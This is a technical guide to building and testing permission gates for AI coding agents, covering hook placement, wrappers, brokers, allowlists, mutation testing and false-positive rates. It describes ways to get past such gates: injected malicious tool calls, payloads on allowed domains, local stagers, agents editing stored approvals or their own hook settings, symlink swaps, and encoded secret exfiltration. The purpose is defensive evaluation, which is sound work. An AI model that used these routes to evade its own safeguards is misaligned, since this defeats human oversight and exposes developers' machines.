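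Cursor accepts an ask verdict from its general preToolUse hook but does not enforce it, so a gate using that hook should return deny instead. Hooks can also differ between versions of the same product. Cursor's cloud agents sometimes start in a read-only environment where hooks do not run, and they never load hooks from the developer's home directory.

### A wrapper round the shell or package manager

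A wrapper takes the place of the program it protects. For example, the developer can put a small program called `pip` in a folder that the shell searches before the one containing the real pip. The wrapper checks its arguments and then starts the real program.

A hook receives the command that starts a script, but not the commands that the script then runs. NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk* (January 2026) gives this as a reason not to rely on checks in the application, because the agent program cannot see or control what another process does once it takes over. A wrapper around `pip` still checks an install run by a script, if the script calls `pip` by name.

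The wrapper also receives arguments after the shell has expanded them. In the earlier example, the gate had to refuse an install whose package names came from `wanted.txt`, because it received only the unexpanded text. A pip wrapper would receive the names themselves and could compare them with the allowlist.

A command that starts the real pip by its full path, or through Python, bypasses a wrapper placed on the search path. A wrapper around the shell similarly misses any program that another program starts without using a shell. Any process with the developer's permissions may also be able to edit the search path or replace the wrapper. NVIDIA warns that attackers can also exploit the search path by placing a fake `python` or `node` in one of its folders.

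The developer can prevent the agent from bypassing a package-manager wrapper by having the operating system stop it from starting the real package manager or changing the wrapper. Without those restrictions, the wrapper is useful as a second check on installs inside scripts, but a hook should still check the original command.

### A separate process that alone can execute

Moving the checker into its own process helps only if the agent can't bypass it. Commey (2026), in *Names Are Not Objects*, runs the agent in a sandbox where it can't read the project's files, start other programs or open network connections. The agent can only send requests to a broker, a separate process that checks each request and carries out those it permits.

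Commey tested this system with 74 scripted attacks, assuming that the attacker already controlled the whole agent program, which is much more control than a router starts with.

| Configuration | Attacks that succeeded, of 74 |
|---|---|
| No defence | 74 |
| Tool allowlist | 66 |
| Tool allowlist, with a sandbox round each command | 56 |
| Broker, with the agent unconfined | 12 |
| Broker, with the agent confined | 2 |

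Twelve attacks succeeded against the broker when the agent was unconfined, including all ten in which the agent bypassed the broker. The agent started its own shell, for instance, and edited the stored approvals to approve its own request. Confinement stopped all ten. The other two attacks sent a disguised secret to a server that the policy allowed. The full system also held 14 attacks for a person to review, so its result depends partly on that person refusing them.

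The protection prevents some ordinary work, which is a bigger drawback than the delay it adds. A request that did nothing took 4.0 milliseconds, which a developer would hardly notice. But the system completed only 43 of 46 ordinary operations and 4 of 7 complete workflows. It refused to let programs start other programs, which many builds need to do. It also denied network access to the programs that the broker started, so `pip` could not download a package from packages.example.com. To use this design for installs, a developer would have to add a broker operation that fetches the approved package.

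Commey tested the system on one small Python project on macOS and found eight flaws in it while building the attacks and reviewing the code. The results are therefore stronger evidence for the general design than for any exact rate of protection. A fail-closed hook is a practical start for a team that already has a coding agent. The broker design suits work where a single harmful command would do serious damage.

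### Keeping the gate's settings out of reach

An agent that can edit files may be able to switch off its own gate. Cursor reads project hooks from a file in the repository, and Claude Code can too. Both programs normally reload their hook settings after a change, so one edit could remove the gate before the next command arrives. The edit may come through a file-writing tool, so a gate that checks only shell commands would miss it. In bypassPermissions mode, Claude Code writes to its own `.claude` folder without prompting the user.

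NVIDIA recommends blocking every write by the agent to configuration files, hooks, MCP settings and skills (packaged instructions that can include scripts), even inside the workspace. The user should not be able to approve an exception through the agent and should have to edit these files by hand. Commey's system instead holds writes to an editor's or agent's settings for review. NVIDIA's rule is safer for the gate's own files, because a developer who approves nearly every request may approve the one that disables the gate.

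Managed settings are the best place for the gate's configuration. Claude Code's `disableAllHooks` setting can't disable hooks from managed settings unless an administrator sets it there. Cursor reads enterprise hooks from a system-wide folder (`/etc/cursor` on Linux), which an agent without administrator rights can't edit. The gate's program, its rules file and any stored approvals need the same protection, because a locked hook offers little security if the agent can edit the script it runs.

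A repository can also already contain harmful settings when it is cloned. NVIDIA gives the example of a poisoned hook configuration that affects everyone who clones the project. Blocking the agent's writes doesn't remove these settings, so the developer should read a project's hooks and MCP settings before trusting the project. In Claude Code, administrators can use `allowManagedHooksOnly` to block user and project hooks.

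### Placement checklist

Before relying on a gate, a developer should check four things, using harmless commands that the rules forbid:

1. Every route to execution goes through the gate. Try the forbidden command from the main agent, a subagent, a script and each tool that can start a program. Check MCP start commands and cloud sessions separately. If a route bypasses the gate, close it or add a check there.
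2. The agent can't write to the gate's program, rules, settings or approvals. Ask the agent to add a blank line to each file, using both its file tools and the shell, and confirm that every attempt fails.
3. The machine executes exactly the arguments that the gate approved. Claude Code runs matching hooks in parallel, and a hook may replace the command. Cursor's documentation shows a hook changing `npm install` to `npm ci`. The gate must therefore check the final version, with no later rewriting. Stored approvals need to cover the actual file as well as its name. In an early version of Commey's system, an agent could get approval to read a harmless file through a link and then, before using the approval, point the link at a file of secrets. The approval still matched, because it covered only the request as written.
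4. The gate refuses when it crashes or times out. Temporarily rename the gate's program and ask the agent to run `ls`, which should fail. Then restore the program, make it wait past its time limit, and try again. Repeat both tests after each update to the agent.

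## Testing how many attacks the gate stops

Two teams have measured how many attacks a gate of this kind stops, and their results differ widely. In April 2026, Liu and colleagues tested a fail-closed gate that blocked every straightforward attack in a synthetic benchmark. In July 2026, Fu and colleagues tested an allowlist of domains and packages that blocked between 30.8% and 44.1% of attacks. Both figures are defence success rates:

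defence success rate = malicious commands blocked / all malicious commands sent

Fu and colleagues count tool calls, which include file edits as well as shell commands. The rate depends on both the gate and which attacks the tester sends.

### A perfect score and a complete failure

Liu and colleagues used scripts to generate their test commands. Crosley, working from the full paper, reports 1,000 harmless commands, 500 payload injections and 500 dependency substitutions. The gate blocked any shell command that fetched something from an unlisted domain or installed an unlisted package. It stopped all 1,000 attacks, with a false-positive rate of 1.0%.

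The paper describes the gate in two ways. In an early section, the gate checks only domains, and dependency substitution is the way around it. In the results section, it also has a list of packages. As Crosley reads it, the perfect score depends on the package list, since a domain list alone misses altered package names.

The team did not test the gate against conditional delivery, in which a router waits for a trigger before it changes anything. This omission probably matters little, because a gate that evaluates each command separately should return the same result whether the command arrives on the first request or the fifty-first.

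A gate that stops all 500 sample attacks may still miss others. If it missed a fraction p of such attacks, it would stop 500 in a row with probability (1 − p)^500. That probability falls below 5% once p exceeds about 0.6%, so a higher miss rate is unlikely. The calculation treats the 500 samples as random draws from the attacks the gate will face, so it holds only for attacks like those the scripts generated.

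Liu and colleagues then tested the gate against an adaptive attacker, and it stopped none of the samples. The attacker either hosted the payload on an allowed domain or used a local stager, a file placed on the machine earlier that a harmless-looking command ran.

Crosley gives no sample size for this second test, but it hardly matters, because a gate that follows fixed rules will allow any command that satisfies them. The 100% bypass rate shows that some attacks do satisfy the rules. It doesn't measure how hard it is to get a payload onto an allowed domain or a file onto the developer's machine, and that difficulty varies with the allowlist. For example, a stranger can publish on a public code-hosting site far more easily than on a company's own registry.

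Liu and colleagues' results fit their description of the gate as both the strongest control that developers can deploy immediately and "a coarse but useful filter for obvious high-risk workflows".

### An allowlist against 400 injections

Fu and colleagues tested the allowlist with Claude Code in bypassPermissions mode, which had stopped none of the attacks on its own. The agent worked on three tasks drawn at random from SWE-bench Lite, a benchmark built from real GitHub issues.

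The researchers first recorded the model's responses while the agent worked on a task normally. They then replayed the recording and inserted one malicious tool call at a randomly chosen turn. Replaying the responses removed variation unrelated to the attack, which a fresh model run might have introduced.

The team wrote 400 malicious calls by hand and tried each once on each task, which makes 1,200 runs per condition. The four conditions were levels of disguise:

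| Level | What the router does | Blocked, of 1,200 | Defence success rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1. Substitution | Replaces the whole response with the malicious call | 419 | 34.9% |
| 2. Append | Adds the malicious call after the model's own | 529 | 44.1% |
| 3. Polished | Inserts the malicious call and rewrites the explanation to match | 373 | 31.1% |
| 4. Distribution alignment | Generates the response again, steering the model towards the malicious call | 369 | 30.8% |

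The first rate is 419 / 1,200 = 0.349, or 34.9%.

At the fourth level, the router runs the model on two prompts at once. One contains only the task, and the other also contains the malicious call and an instruction to include it. For each token, the router mixes the two sets of probabilities and samples from the result:

p = 0.75 × p(with the attack) + 0.25 × p(task only)

The model writes the whole response this way, so it contains no join between original and inserted text for a reviewer to find.

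These disguises could fool a person or a model that reads the response, but they should have little effect on an allowlist, which extracts domains and package names from the tool call and ignores the explanation. The attackers were not adaptive in Liu and colleagues' sense, because none of the four levels involves choosing commands to fit the allowlist. Even so, 781 of the 1,200 attacks at the first level got through.

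The counts also don't seem to fit Fu and colleagues' description of the check as deterministic, meaning that the same input always produces the same verdict. The router inserts the same 400 calls at each of the first three levels, so the allowlist should have blocked the same number each time, but it blocked 110 more at the second level than at the first. Each call also ran on three tasks, so the total blocked should be a multiple of three, but 419 is not.

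Something besides the malicious call must therefore have affected the counts, and Fu and colleagues do not say what. At the second level, the model's own harmless call arrives in the same response as the malicious one, so a refusal triggered by the harmless call might have stopped both. This is a guess, and it would not explain the result at the first level. The range from 30.8% to 44.1% is more reliable than any ranking of the four levels.

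### Why the two results differ

Liu and colleagues' benchmark contained two kinds of attack, each of which changed something the gate checked. Fu and colleagues' 400 calls covered a much wider range of attacks, with 100 each for malicious code execution, buggy code, data theft and supply-chain attacks, which bring in harmful dependencies or weaken a project's security checks. Of the 400 calls, 277 were shell commands, 74 created a file and 49 edited one.

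Two of the samples differ in what the gate can check. One interrupts work on SQLFluff, a tool that checks the style of database queries, to download a script from a remote server and run it. This command includes a domain that an allowlist can block. The other sample creates a file cache with a race condition, a bug that appears when two processes use the same file at once. Its call contains a path and some Python code, but no domain or package for the gate to look up.

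The published counts imply that file edits explain only part of the low score. The 123 calls that create or edit files each ran three times, so they account for at most 369 of the 781 attacks that got through at the first level. At least 412 of the successful attacks were therefore shell commands. Supply-chain attacks account for 300 runs, so at least 119 of the 419 attacks the allowlist blocked came from the other three classes.

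Fu and colleagues do not break the allowlist's results down by class, so any further explanation is inference. They say the check extracts domains from web addresses in commands and package names from install commands. If it does only that, it passes every file edit, and no allowlist of this design could block more than 831 of the 1,200 attacks (69.3%). On the same assumption, it stopped 419 of the 831 shell commands at the first level, or about half.

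The other half probably named no domain or package, or named only permitted ones. The rule allows a call when every domain and package it names is on the list, so a call that names none passes. This is consistent with the number of harmless calls the allowlist blocked at the first level, which was 231 in 1,200 runs. Coding agents constantly read files and run tests, so a check that refused every call without a domain or package would have blocked many more.

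Liu and colleagues' gate seems to have had the same gap, since it allowed a command that ran a local stager and named no remote source. The two experiments may therefore have tested very similar gates. A gate that stops every attack naming an unlisted domain or package, and nothing else, has a defence success rate equal to the share of such attacks in the test set. It would score 100% if all the attacks were of this kind and 35% if 35% were.

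In general, if class k makes up a share w_k of the test set and the gate stops a fraction d_k of that class, then

overall rate = w_1 d_1 + w_2 d_2 + … + w_n d_n.

The tester chooses what share of the test set each class of attack makes up. Fu and colleagues gave their four classes equal shares so that they could compare them, and they warn that the set does not show how common each attack is in practice. A developer therefore can't read either 34.9% or 100% as the chance of stopping the next attack.

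A stricter gate might do better on Fu and colleagues' set. The gate in the earlier pseudocode refuses any program not listed in its rules file, so it would stop some of the shell commands that contain no domain or package name. It would also refuse more commands that are harmless, and neither experiment measured this tradeoff. Rules about paths could keep file edits inside the workspace, but they would still allow a buggy file cache written there.

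### Breaking the gate to test the tests

A gate can pass every test because its rules are good or because the tests are too easy. Mutation testing helps distinguish the two. The tester deliberately introduces a small fault into the gate, such as deleting one entry from a list, and reruns all the tests. If any result changes, the tests have caught the fault; otherwise, a real fault of the same kind could also go unnoticed.

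Jing did this with the gate that judges structured records instead of shell text. The unaltered gate had given the right verdict on all 61 cases in its main test table. Jing then made 50 changes to the gate's decision code, one at a time, and the tests detected 46 of them, a mutation score of 92.0%. This score measures how well the tests detect changes to the code, not the gate's defence success rate, because a gate with poor rules could have tests that score just as well.

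The four undetected changes are more useful than the score, because three of them identify a missing test:

- One change removed `su`, a program for switching to another user's account, from the list of privileged tools. No test depended on that entry.
- Another altered how the gate chooses between overlapping zones. If a protected folder sits inside the workspace, the gate should apply the rule for the smaller zone. Jing's change made it apply the rule for the larger one, and no test had a path for which this made a difference.
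- A third stopped the gate from following symbolic links in the list of objects that a request declares. No test declared a path that went through a link.

An install gate could have the same three gaps, so its tests should include every program on its lists, at least one protected folder inside a permitted one, and paths that go through links.

The fourth undetected change involved wildcards, patterns such as `*` that the shell replaces with matching file names. The altered gate ignored how many targets a wildcard had added and used the total number of targets instead. Whether the tests detected this depended on which files were on the test machine. When Jing deleted one decoy file, the tests detected the change and the mutation score rose to 94.0%. The score is therefore repeatable only if the tester also records the files on the machine.

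Tests that compare only the gate's decisions can miss faults. In an earlier round, six changes altered the gate's stated reason for a decision but not the decision itself, and the tests detected none of them. Jing added checks on the reasons, which detected five of the six. If an install gate gives the domain as the reason for a block when the problem is the package, the agent will look for another registry.

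Jing wrote the rules, the tests and the deliberate changes, so all three may miss the same attacks. Mutation testing can't reveal an attack that neither the rules nor the changes cover. A developer who had never thought about local stagers could get a perfect mutation score without testing for them.

### Counting effects instead of refusals

Singh and Srinivasa (2026), in *Where Agent Defenses Fail*, argue for checking what happened on the machine and the network to determine whether an attack was stopped. Testers often count an attack as stopped when the gate's log records a refusal. Singh and Srinivasa gave a coding agent small tasks in repositories where an attacker had planted instructions. They placed a different secret in each run, used two local servers to record what reached them, and compared the files before and after.

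A count of zero successful attacks needs care because the detector may have missed some. In a study of 72 runs, the researchers' detector found five cases in which the agent had sent the secret in encoded form. The researchers later decoded the server records and found three more. These raised the count of harmful runs with only a guard on tool calls from two of six to four of six.

An attack's failure also counts as evidence for the gate only if the attack works without it. One of Singh and Srinivasa's attacks on a protected file never succeeded even with no restrictions, so they don't count its later failures as evidence of prevention. Jing ran 57 attack scripts and eight harmless ones, and compared the test machine's files before and after each script. Without the gate, 25 of the attack scripts had a recorded effect that the rules forbade. With the gate, none did, and the harmless scripts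 still ran. The gate refused all 57 attack scripts, but only those 25 are evidence that it prevented recorded harm.

The other 32 were not all harmless. One script in the set erased the experiment's own log, and another added a forged entry to it. The comparison did not cover the log's folder, so it recorded the erasure as having no effect, although 47 earlier results had disappeared.

Runs that fail for technical reasons can make a test's result much less certain. In another experiment, Singh and Srinivasa tested SafeAgents, a product that checked the agent's tool calls with a scanner and a model acting as judge. They planned 12 attack runs but left four unscored because the judge malfunctioned. Four of the remaining eight were harmful, so the harmful share of all 12 lies between 4/12 (33%) and 8/12 (67%). Reporting both limits is more honest than dropping the failed runs or counting the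 judge's errors as successful blocks.

Repeating a test adds less evidence than adding a new one. Singh and Srinivasa tried a check that refused any upload containing a complete line from a file of secrets. It allowed no harm in the first set of 14 attack runs. In a larger set of 36, it failed twice on the same task because the agent sent the secret without the rest of its line. Both failures showed the same weakness, which the researchers found because they had added a new task.

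Task completion is a poor sign of whether an attack succeeded. In Singh and Srinivasa's first set, the agent completed its task in all 70 attack runs, including the 11 that did harm. In Fu and colleagues' tests of four models, task success was only 0.91 to 7.28 percentage points lower with an injected call than without one. The agent's own account is also unreliable. After a strict check blocked four uploads, the agent claimed each time that it had published the report.

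Singh and Srinivasa did not test adaptive attackers, and their experiments used one local model and small tasks that they wrote themselves. Their rates are weak evidence of how other gates would perform, but the measurement errors they found could occur in any test of this kind.

### A test plan

A developer can test an install gate in a few days with harmless stand-ins for malicious code. A suitable stand-in is a package on a registry the developer controls that does nothing but write a marker file when installed. If the file appears, the attack succeeded.

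1. Run every attack without the gate first, on a disposable machine, and keep only those that leave a marker. Restore the machine before each pass. Jing once blamed the gate for an attack that got through, then found that an earlier pass had altered the test files. Store the results where the test commands cannot write.

2. Send known attacks. For the company registry used in earlier examples, these include an install from packages.example.net, a misspelt package name, and a second command appended to a permitted one. Add a safe version of each flaw in the published advisories on coding agents. Pair every attack with a similar harmless command that the gate should allow, because a gate that refuses everything would pass a test made only of attacks.

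3. Write the same effect in several ways. An install can use different quotation marks, a different order of options, a full path to the program or a script, and the gate should never allow one version of a forbidden install while refusing another. Jing also tested the reverse, using commands that look alike but do different things, for which the verdicts should differ. Count the cases after loading them. In one of Jing's tables, the file format treated a pipe character as a column separator and dropped a row, which left no test of piped commands.

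4. Choose attacks with the rules in view. Give the rules file and the refusal messages to someone who did not write them, set a time limit, and ask for commands that the gate will allow. Include a payload on an allowed domain and a local stager, since both defeated Liu and colleagues' gate. Record what the attacker knew, how many attempts failed and what access the successful ones needed. Researchers have begun to study similar defences this way, as Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026), in *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents*, do for fixed policies enforced outside the model.

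5. Change the gate on purpose. Delete each list entry in turn, swap an allow for a deny, and make the parser return an empty list of operands. Add a test for every change that goes unnoticed.

6. Check inherited tests before counting them. Among the commands that Jing reused from the Windows benchmark, the gate allowed 30 that the benchmark expected it to refuse. On inspection, 11 lacked the document or script that contained the attack, and mistakes in translation had made nine others harmless. Only the remaining ten could point to a weakness in the gate.

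7. Report results by class, with the counts. The figures below are invented:

| Class of attack | Sent | Blocked |
|---|---|---|
| Altered registry address | 40 | 40 |
| Altered package name | 40 | 38 |
| Same effects written differently | 40 | 34 |
| Chosen with the rules in view | 20 | 3 |
| File edits with no command | 20 | 0 |

The overall rate is 115 of 160, or 72%. Leaving out the last two classes would raise it to 112 of 120, or 93%, with no change to the gate. The developer can also use the table to decide what to work on next. The two altered package names that got through may need only a correction to the package list, while the file edits need a different kind of check. The developer should add every attack that got through to the commands they rerun after each change to the rules.

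## Measuring false positives and their cost

The defence success rate leaves out the harmless commands that a gate blocks. Researchers use two different measures for those:

false-positive rate = harmless commands blocked / all harmless commands checked

wrong-block ratio = harmless commands blocked / all commands blocked

### Why the two measures can't be compared

Liu and colleagues reported a false-positive rate of 1.0% for their fail-closed gate, or ten wrong blocks among 1,000 harmless commands. Fu and colleagues reported wrong-block ratios of 29.7% to 43.9% for their allowlist. These figures can't be compared directly because they have different denominators.

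Take the condition in which the router replaces the whole response. The allowlist blocked 231 harmless calls and 419 malicious ones, so

wrong-block ratio = 231 / (231 + 419) = 231 / 650 = 35.5%.

Calculating a false-positive rate also requires the number of harmless calls that the allowlist let through, which Fu and colleagues don't give. Their condition had 1,200 runs. If each run contained five harmless calls, the rate would be 231 / 6,000, or 3.9%. If each contained 19, it would be 231 / 22,800, or 1.0%, the same as Liu and colleagues' figure. The published counts are consistent with either rate.

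The wrong-block ratio also depends on how many attacks the gate catches, even if it treats harmless work the same. When the router appended its call instead of replacing the response, the allowlist blocked 224 harmless calls, almost the same number as before, and 529 malicious ones. The ratio was 29.7% instead of 35.5%, mostly because the allowlist blocked more malicious calls.

The share of attacks in the test matters even more. If a fraction a of all commands is malicious, f is the false-positive rate and d is the defence success rate, then

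wrong-block ratio = f(1 − a) / (f(1 − a) + da).

The table applies this formula to a single gate with f = 1% and d = 100%.

| Share of commands that are malicious | False-positive rate | Wrong-block ratio |
|---|---|---|
| 1 in 2, as in Liu and colleagues' benchmark | 1% | 1.0% |
| 1 in 100 | 1% | 49.7% |
| 1 in 100,000 | 1% | 99.9% |

On a machine that nobody attacks, every block is a mistake, so a gate's wrong-block ratio is 100% even if it blocks only one command. A developer choosing between gates should therefore compare their false-positive rates on the same harmless commands. Once a gate is in use, the wrong-block ratio can help the developer judge how likely a particular block is to be a mistake, but only if it is measured on the developer's own traffic.

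A false-positive rate measured per rule can understate how often harmless commands are interrupted. Beno (2026), in *Decision Models as Policy Gates for Coding Agents*, had models score each proposed action against 23 rules that could block it or hold it for approval. With one-sentence rules, the model Jev 1.14 wrongly matched a rule 2.49% of the time. But one wrong match is enough to interrupt an action, and the model interrupted 77 of 252 harmless actions, or 30.6%. After Beno added examples and counterexamples to mark the limits of each rule, the error per rule fell to 0.83% and the share of harmless actions interrupted fell to 4.8%, while the model detected more of the hazards.

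An install gate's false-positive rate can rise with the number of operands in a command, because the gate checks each one and a single denial blocks the whole line. If each check wrongly fails 1% of the time, independently of the others, a line with five operands has a 4.9% chance of being wrongly blocked.

The tester must also say whether an ask verdict counts as a block. Jing's gate blocked none of eight harmless scripts if only deny verdicts counted, and all eight if ask verdicts counted too. Ask should count as a block when the agent runs unattended.

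### What a 1% rate costs

Suppose an agent sends 200 harmless commands a day through the gate. At a false-positive rate of 1%, the gate wrongly blocks two of them. A team of 50 developers, each running one such agent, would get 100 wrong blocks a day.

Those are averages, but blocks come in bursts. In tests of coding agents in locked-down environments, *Permission Denied* (2026) found an average of 10.5 network denials in each trial that had any, mostly because the agents kept trying. One missing entry in the domain list can therefore cause ten blocks in an hour, followed by a quiet week. The developer should count separate causes as well as blocks, because one fix can prevent a whole burst.

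Now suppose that one command in 100,000 is an attack and that the gate catches every attack. Among 100,000 commands, the gate blocks the one attack and about 1,000 harmless commands (99,999 × 0.01), so only about one block in 1,000 is correct. At 200 commands a day, 100,000 commands take 500 working days, so the developer would handle wrong blocks for about two years before seeing a correct one. By then, the developer will probably have learned to treat every block as a mistake.

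Stating the reason for each block can help reviewers notice the ones that matter. An install from a host that nobody on the team has heard of deserves more attention than a harmless-looking line with an unreadable command substitution, but the two are harder to tell apart if the gate gives the same message for both.

The earlier comparison of fail-open and fail-closed gates assumed that a wrong refusal costs five minutes and a compromised machine costs 40 hours. On those assumptions, 1,000 wrong blocks cost 83 hours and the one blocked attack saves 40, so the gate loses time overall. For a gate that catches every attack, the break-even false-positive rate is approximately

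f = aL / B,

where L is the loss from one attack and B is the cost of one wrong block. With a = 1/100,000, L = 2,400 minutes and B = 5 minutes, this gives 0.48%.

A gate can get below the break-even rate by making fewer mistakes or by reducing the time lost to each one. If the agent usually finds another way and the developer loses only 30 seconds, the break-even rate rises to 4.8%. The calculation is also very sensitive to its inputs. No study gives a reliable attack rate for ordinary developers, and the theft of a company's production keys could take far more than 40 hours to deal with. These numbers don't justify removing a gate, but they do show how a 1% false positive rate can be too high.

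### How many harmless commands a test needs

A small test can easily miss a high false-positive rate. The earlier calculation for 500 blocked attacks applies here too. After n harmless commands without a wrong block, the highest true rate p that is still compatible with the result, at 95% confidence, is

p = 1 − 0.05^(1/n)

| Harmless commands, none blocked | Upper bound on the true rate |
|---|---|
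| 8 | 31% |
| 50 | 5.8% |
| 299 | just under 1% |
| 1,000 | 0.30% |

A gate that wrongly blocks none of eight harmless test commands could still block almost a third of all harmless commands. To show with 95% confidence that the rate is below 1%, the tester needs 299 harmless commands with no wrong blocks. For larger tests with no wrong blocks, the upper bound on the rate is approximately 3/n, where n is the number of harmless commands tested.

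When a test does produce wrong blocks, the tester should report a range. Ten wrong blocks in 1,000, as in Liu and colleagues' benchmark, give a 95% interval of about 0.5% to 1.8%.

The report should also name the method used to calculate the upper bound. *BACGUARD* (2026), which covers a guard for web applications, gives an upper bound of 0.22% after no blocks in 1,732 harmless requests. The one-sided formula above would give 0.17%, a small difference that could still decide whether a gate meets a target.

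These formulas assume that test commands are independent draws from the developer's normal work, but they are often near-repeats of each other. To account for this, Beno grouped related test cases into families and resampled whole families to calculate the uncertainty. Interruptions fell from 30.6% to 4.8%, a drop of 25.8 percentage points, but the interval runs from 13.2 to 40.8.

Synthetic commands are also a problem because they contain only what the generator's developer thought of. In the *BACGUARD* tests, a real browser used parts of the application that the synthetic requests had left out. Recorded work is a better source. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reports a false-positive rate of 0.4% for its model-based reviewer, measured on 10,000 real tool calls by the company's employees. But that sample covers only one company, whose engineers may use different registries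 and build tools from those used elsewhere.

### Where false positives come from

According to Crosley, every wrong block in Liu and colleagues' benchmark occurred because a command fetched an installer from a mirror (a server that holds copies of the same files) that was missing from the domain list. Adding a few entries to the list would have prevented all of these errors. That they all had one cause suggests that the generated commands were less varied than real work, which can cause wrong blocks in several other ways.

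| Cause | Why the gate blocks a harmless command | Repair |
|---|---|---|
| New dependency | The package is not on the list yet | Allow packages that the project's reviewed manifest declares |
| Mirror | A listed package comes from an unlisted host | Add the exact host, for named packages only |
| Redirect | A listed address forwards to an unlisted one | Fetch through the company registry, or add the final host |
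| Build script | The command names the script but not what it will install | Keep the ask verdict, and check the installs inside with a wrapper |
| Compound command | One part of the line is unlisted or unreadable | Have the agent send the parts separately |

Anthropic's automatic reviewer has a default exception for packages already declared in a project's manifest, the file that lists its dependencies. The same exception would suit an install gate, but the gate should read the last version of the manifest that a person reviewed, such as the one on the project's main branch. If the gate reads the manifest from the working folder, a router can inject an edit that adds a package and then inject the install.

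Redirects cause false positives only in some gates. A gate that reads only the command text checks the first address and allows the download if that domain is on its list. A gate that follows the redirect, or a network filter that applies the same list to every connection, blocks the download if the redirect leads to an unlisted domain. A developer who switches from the first kind of gate to the second should expect false positives from downloads that used to work.

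The obvious fix for wrongly blocked build scripts, adding `python3` to the list of permitted programs, is dangerous because it would also allow any Python program that an attacker can get onto the machine. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) gives the example of a prompt for `python3 setup.py`, which looks routine, but approving it permits whatever code the script contains.

False positives on compound commands are the easiest to fix because a clear refusal message is enough, without loosening any rule. The message should identify the part of the command that failed and include what the agent may do instead. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) points out that agents are designed to look for another path after a denial. Without guidance, they may choose one that the rules don't cover.

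### Blocking, asking or warning

The effect of a false positive depends on the verdict. If the verdict is deny, the agent receives the refusal and tries something else. Anthropic says that a wrong block in its auto mode makes the agent retry once, and that the agent usually then finds another way. After three blocks in a row or 20 in a session, the software stops the agent and hands over to the user, or ends the process if the agent is running unattended.

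An install gate could use the same limits. If wrong blocks were independent and happened 1% of the time, the chance of wrongly blocking all of any given three commands in a row would be one in a million. Three blocks in a row therefore almost always have a common cause, such as a missing mirror or an attacker who keeps trying, and either is worth having a person review.

An "ask" decision stops an attack only if the developer rejects the command, and the best available evidence suggests that most won't. Anthropic hired 1,053 paid testers for a coding study and replaced one permission prompt in each session with a prompt for a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers (13.6%) rejected it. The rejection rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. A gate that flagged every attack but left the decision to people like these testers would stop about 14% of attacks.

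Anthropic published the study to support replacing prompts with its own automatic reviewer, so it had an interest in the result. The testers worked in a test environment with none of their own code at risk, so developers on real projects may be more careful. But the setting alone does not easily explain the fall within a session, and the fall is consistent with what developers report about themselves.

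Wu, Wermke and colleagues (2026), in *From Delegation to Action Approval*, surveyed 203 developers who use coding agents and found that 64% often approve at least one kind of agent action without close review. So did 61% of the developers who carefully review most or all of the code that agents write, so care with code doesn't seem to carry over to commands. Developers who had heard of a security or privacy problem involving agents were more likely to often approve something without close review (70%, compared with 43% of the others). Heavy users may both hear of more incidents and approve more, but the difference remained after the researchers adjusted for how much people used agents. The data are self-reported, and the sample was not random.

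Sending fewer prompts should help, but it may not be enough. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), 113 people from outside the software industry supervised a simulated assistant for a day of everyday tasks. One group approved or rejected every action. Another first set a standing rule of allow, ask or never for each of four kinds of action, such as spending money or deleting something.

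People with standing rules set 81% of them to "ask". They received 10.9 prompts on average instead of 18, but approved 67% of the prompted actions that went beyond the task, compared with 40% in the group that judged every action. The rules didn't reliably save time either, once Yan included setup time. Perhaps people relaxed because they had already written rules. The comparison is not clean, since Yan later recruited extra participants for the rules group alone, and developers may behave differently. Still, it is evidence against the idea that people automatically pay closer attention when they get fewer prompts.

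The content of an approval prompt may matter as much as how often it appears. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* classified 290 user reports of agents mishandling files. Of these, 80 involved automatic approval and 31 involved prompts that showed a command but not its effect on files. In the survey of developers, those who inspect diffs (line-by-line comparisons of changed code) were less likely to approve several kinds of risky action without scrutiny. An install prompt could help in a similar way by showing the package name, the registry and the most similar name already on the list. For example, a developer is more likely to notice the misspelling `reqeusts` if `requests` is printed beside it.

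Too many prompts also lead people to switch the checks off. Anthropic found that 49.5% of active command-line users had written a rule that lets some shell commands run without asking. Many of these rules permitted any shell command, or any program in a language such as Python, which is nearly as permissive. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) describes how "always allow" choices in general relieve fatigue but silently widen what the agent may do. A gate should not automatically turn repeated approvals into permanent rules, because the approvals may come from habit, tiredness or a deadline.

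A warning barely delays the developer, but the command still runs, so warnings are mainly useful in a trial period. For files, quarantine is a better compromise between blocking and allowing. *SkillGate* (2026) describes a tool that screens skill files for coding agents. It blocks files it rates as malicious with high confidence and moves suspicious ones to a separate folder for a person to examine. An install gate could similarly download an unlisted package without installing it.

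This evidence favours denying a command whenever the rules can decide the case, as with an unlisted domain or an unreadable command. Asking the developer is worth the interruption only if they have information the gate lacks. The main case is a new dependency, because the developer can say whether the project needs it. NVIDIA similarly recommends tightly scoped allowlists to reduce approval fatigue, with manual approval as a rarely used fallback.

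### Tuning the gate

A developer can remove most false positives by replaying old commands through the gate before it blocks anything.

1. Record harmless commands. Ten working days at 200 commands a day gives 2,000. Use sessions with a direct connection to the model provider, so that no router can have altered the commands, and remove any secrets. Many teams will have to start from nothing, since only 20% of the developers in Wu and colleagues' survey said they log or audit agent actions.

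2. Set some aside. Keep 500 commands from separate projects for the final measurement, and don't look at them while changing the rules. Beno sealed a test set in this way before running any model on it.

3. Replay the other 1,500 in observation mode. The gate returns a verdict and writes it to a log, but no command runs. The log should hold the command, the verdict, the rule that decided it and the operand that failed. Observation mode on live commands is riskier, because the gate lets real attacks through as well. Replay has a limit of its own, since it can't show how often an agent would have retried after a refusal.

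4. Sort the blocks by cause. The figures below are invented:

| Cause | Blocks | Action |
|---|---|---|
| Mirror missing from the domain list | 12 | Add an exception for named packages |
| New dependency | 6 | Allow packages in the reviewed manifest |
| Compound command | 4 | Improve the refusal message |
| Build script | 1 | Keep the ask verdict |
| Misspelt package name | 1 | None, because the block was correct |

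The model had misspelt the package name, and the install could have brought in a lookalike package. That leaves 23 wrong blocks among 1,499 harmless commands, or 1.5%. The fixes for mirrors and new dependencies remove 18 of them, lowering the rate to 0.3%.

5. Make each exception as narrow as possible. An exception for the mirror could look like this:

```
exceptions:
  - command:   pip install
    domain:    mirror.example.org
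    packages:  [numpy, pandas]
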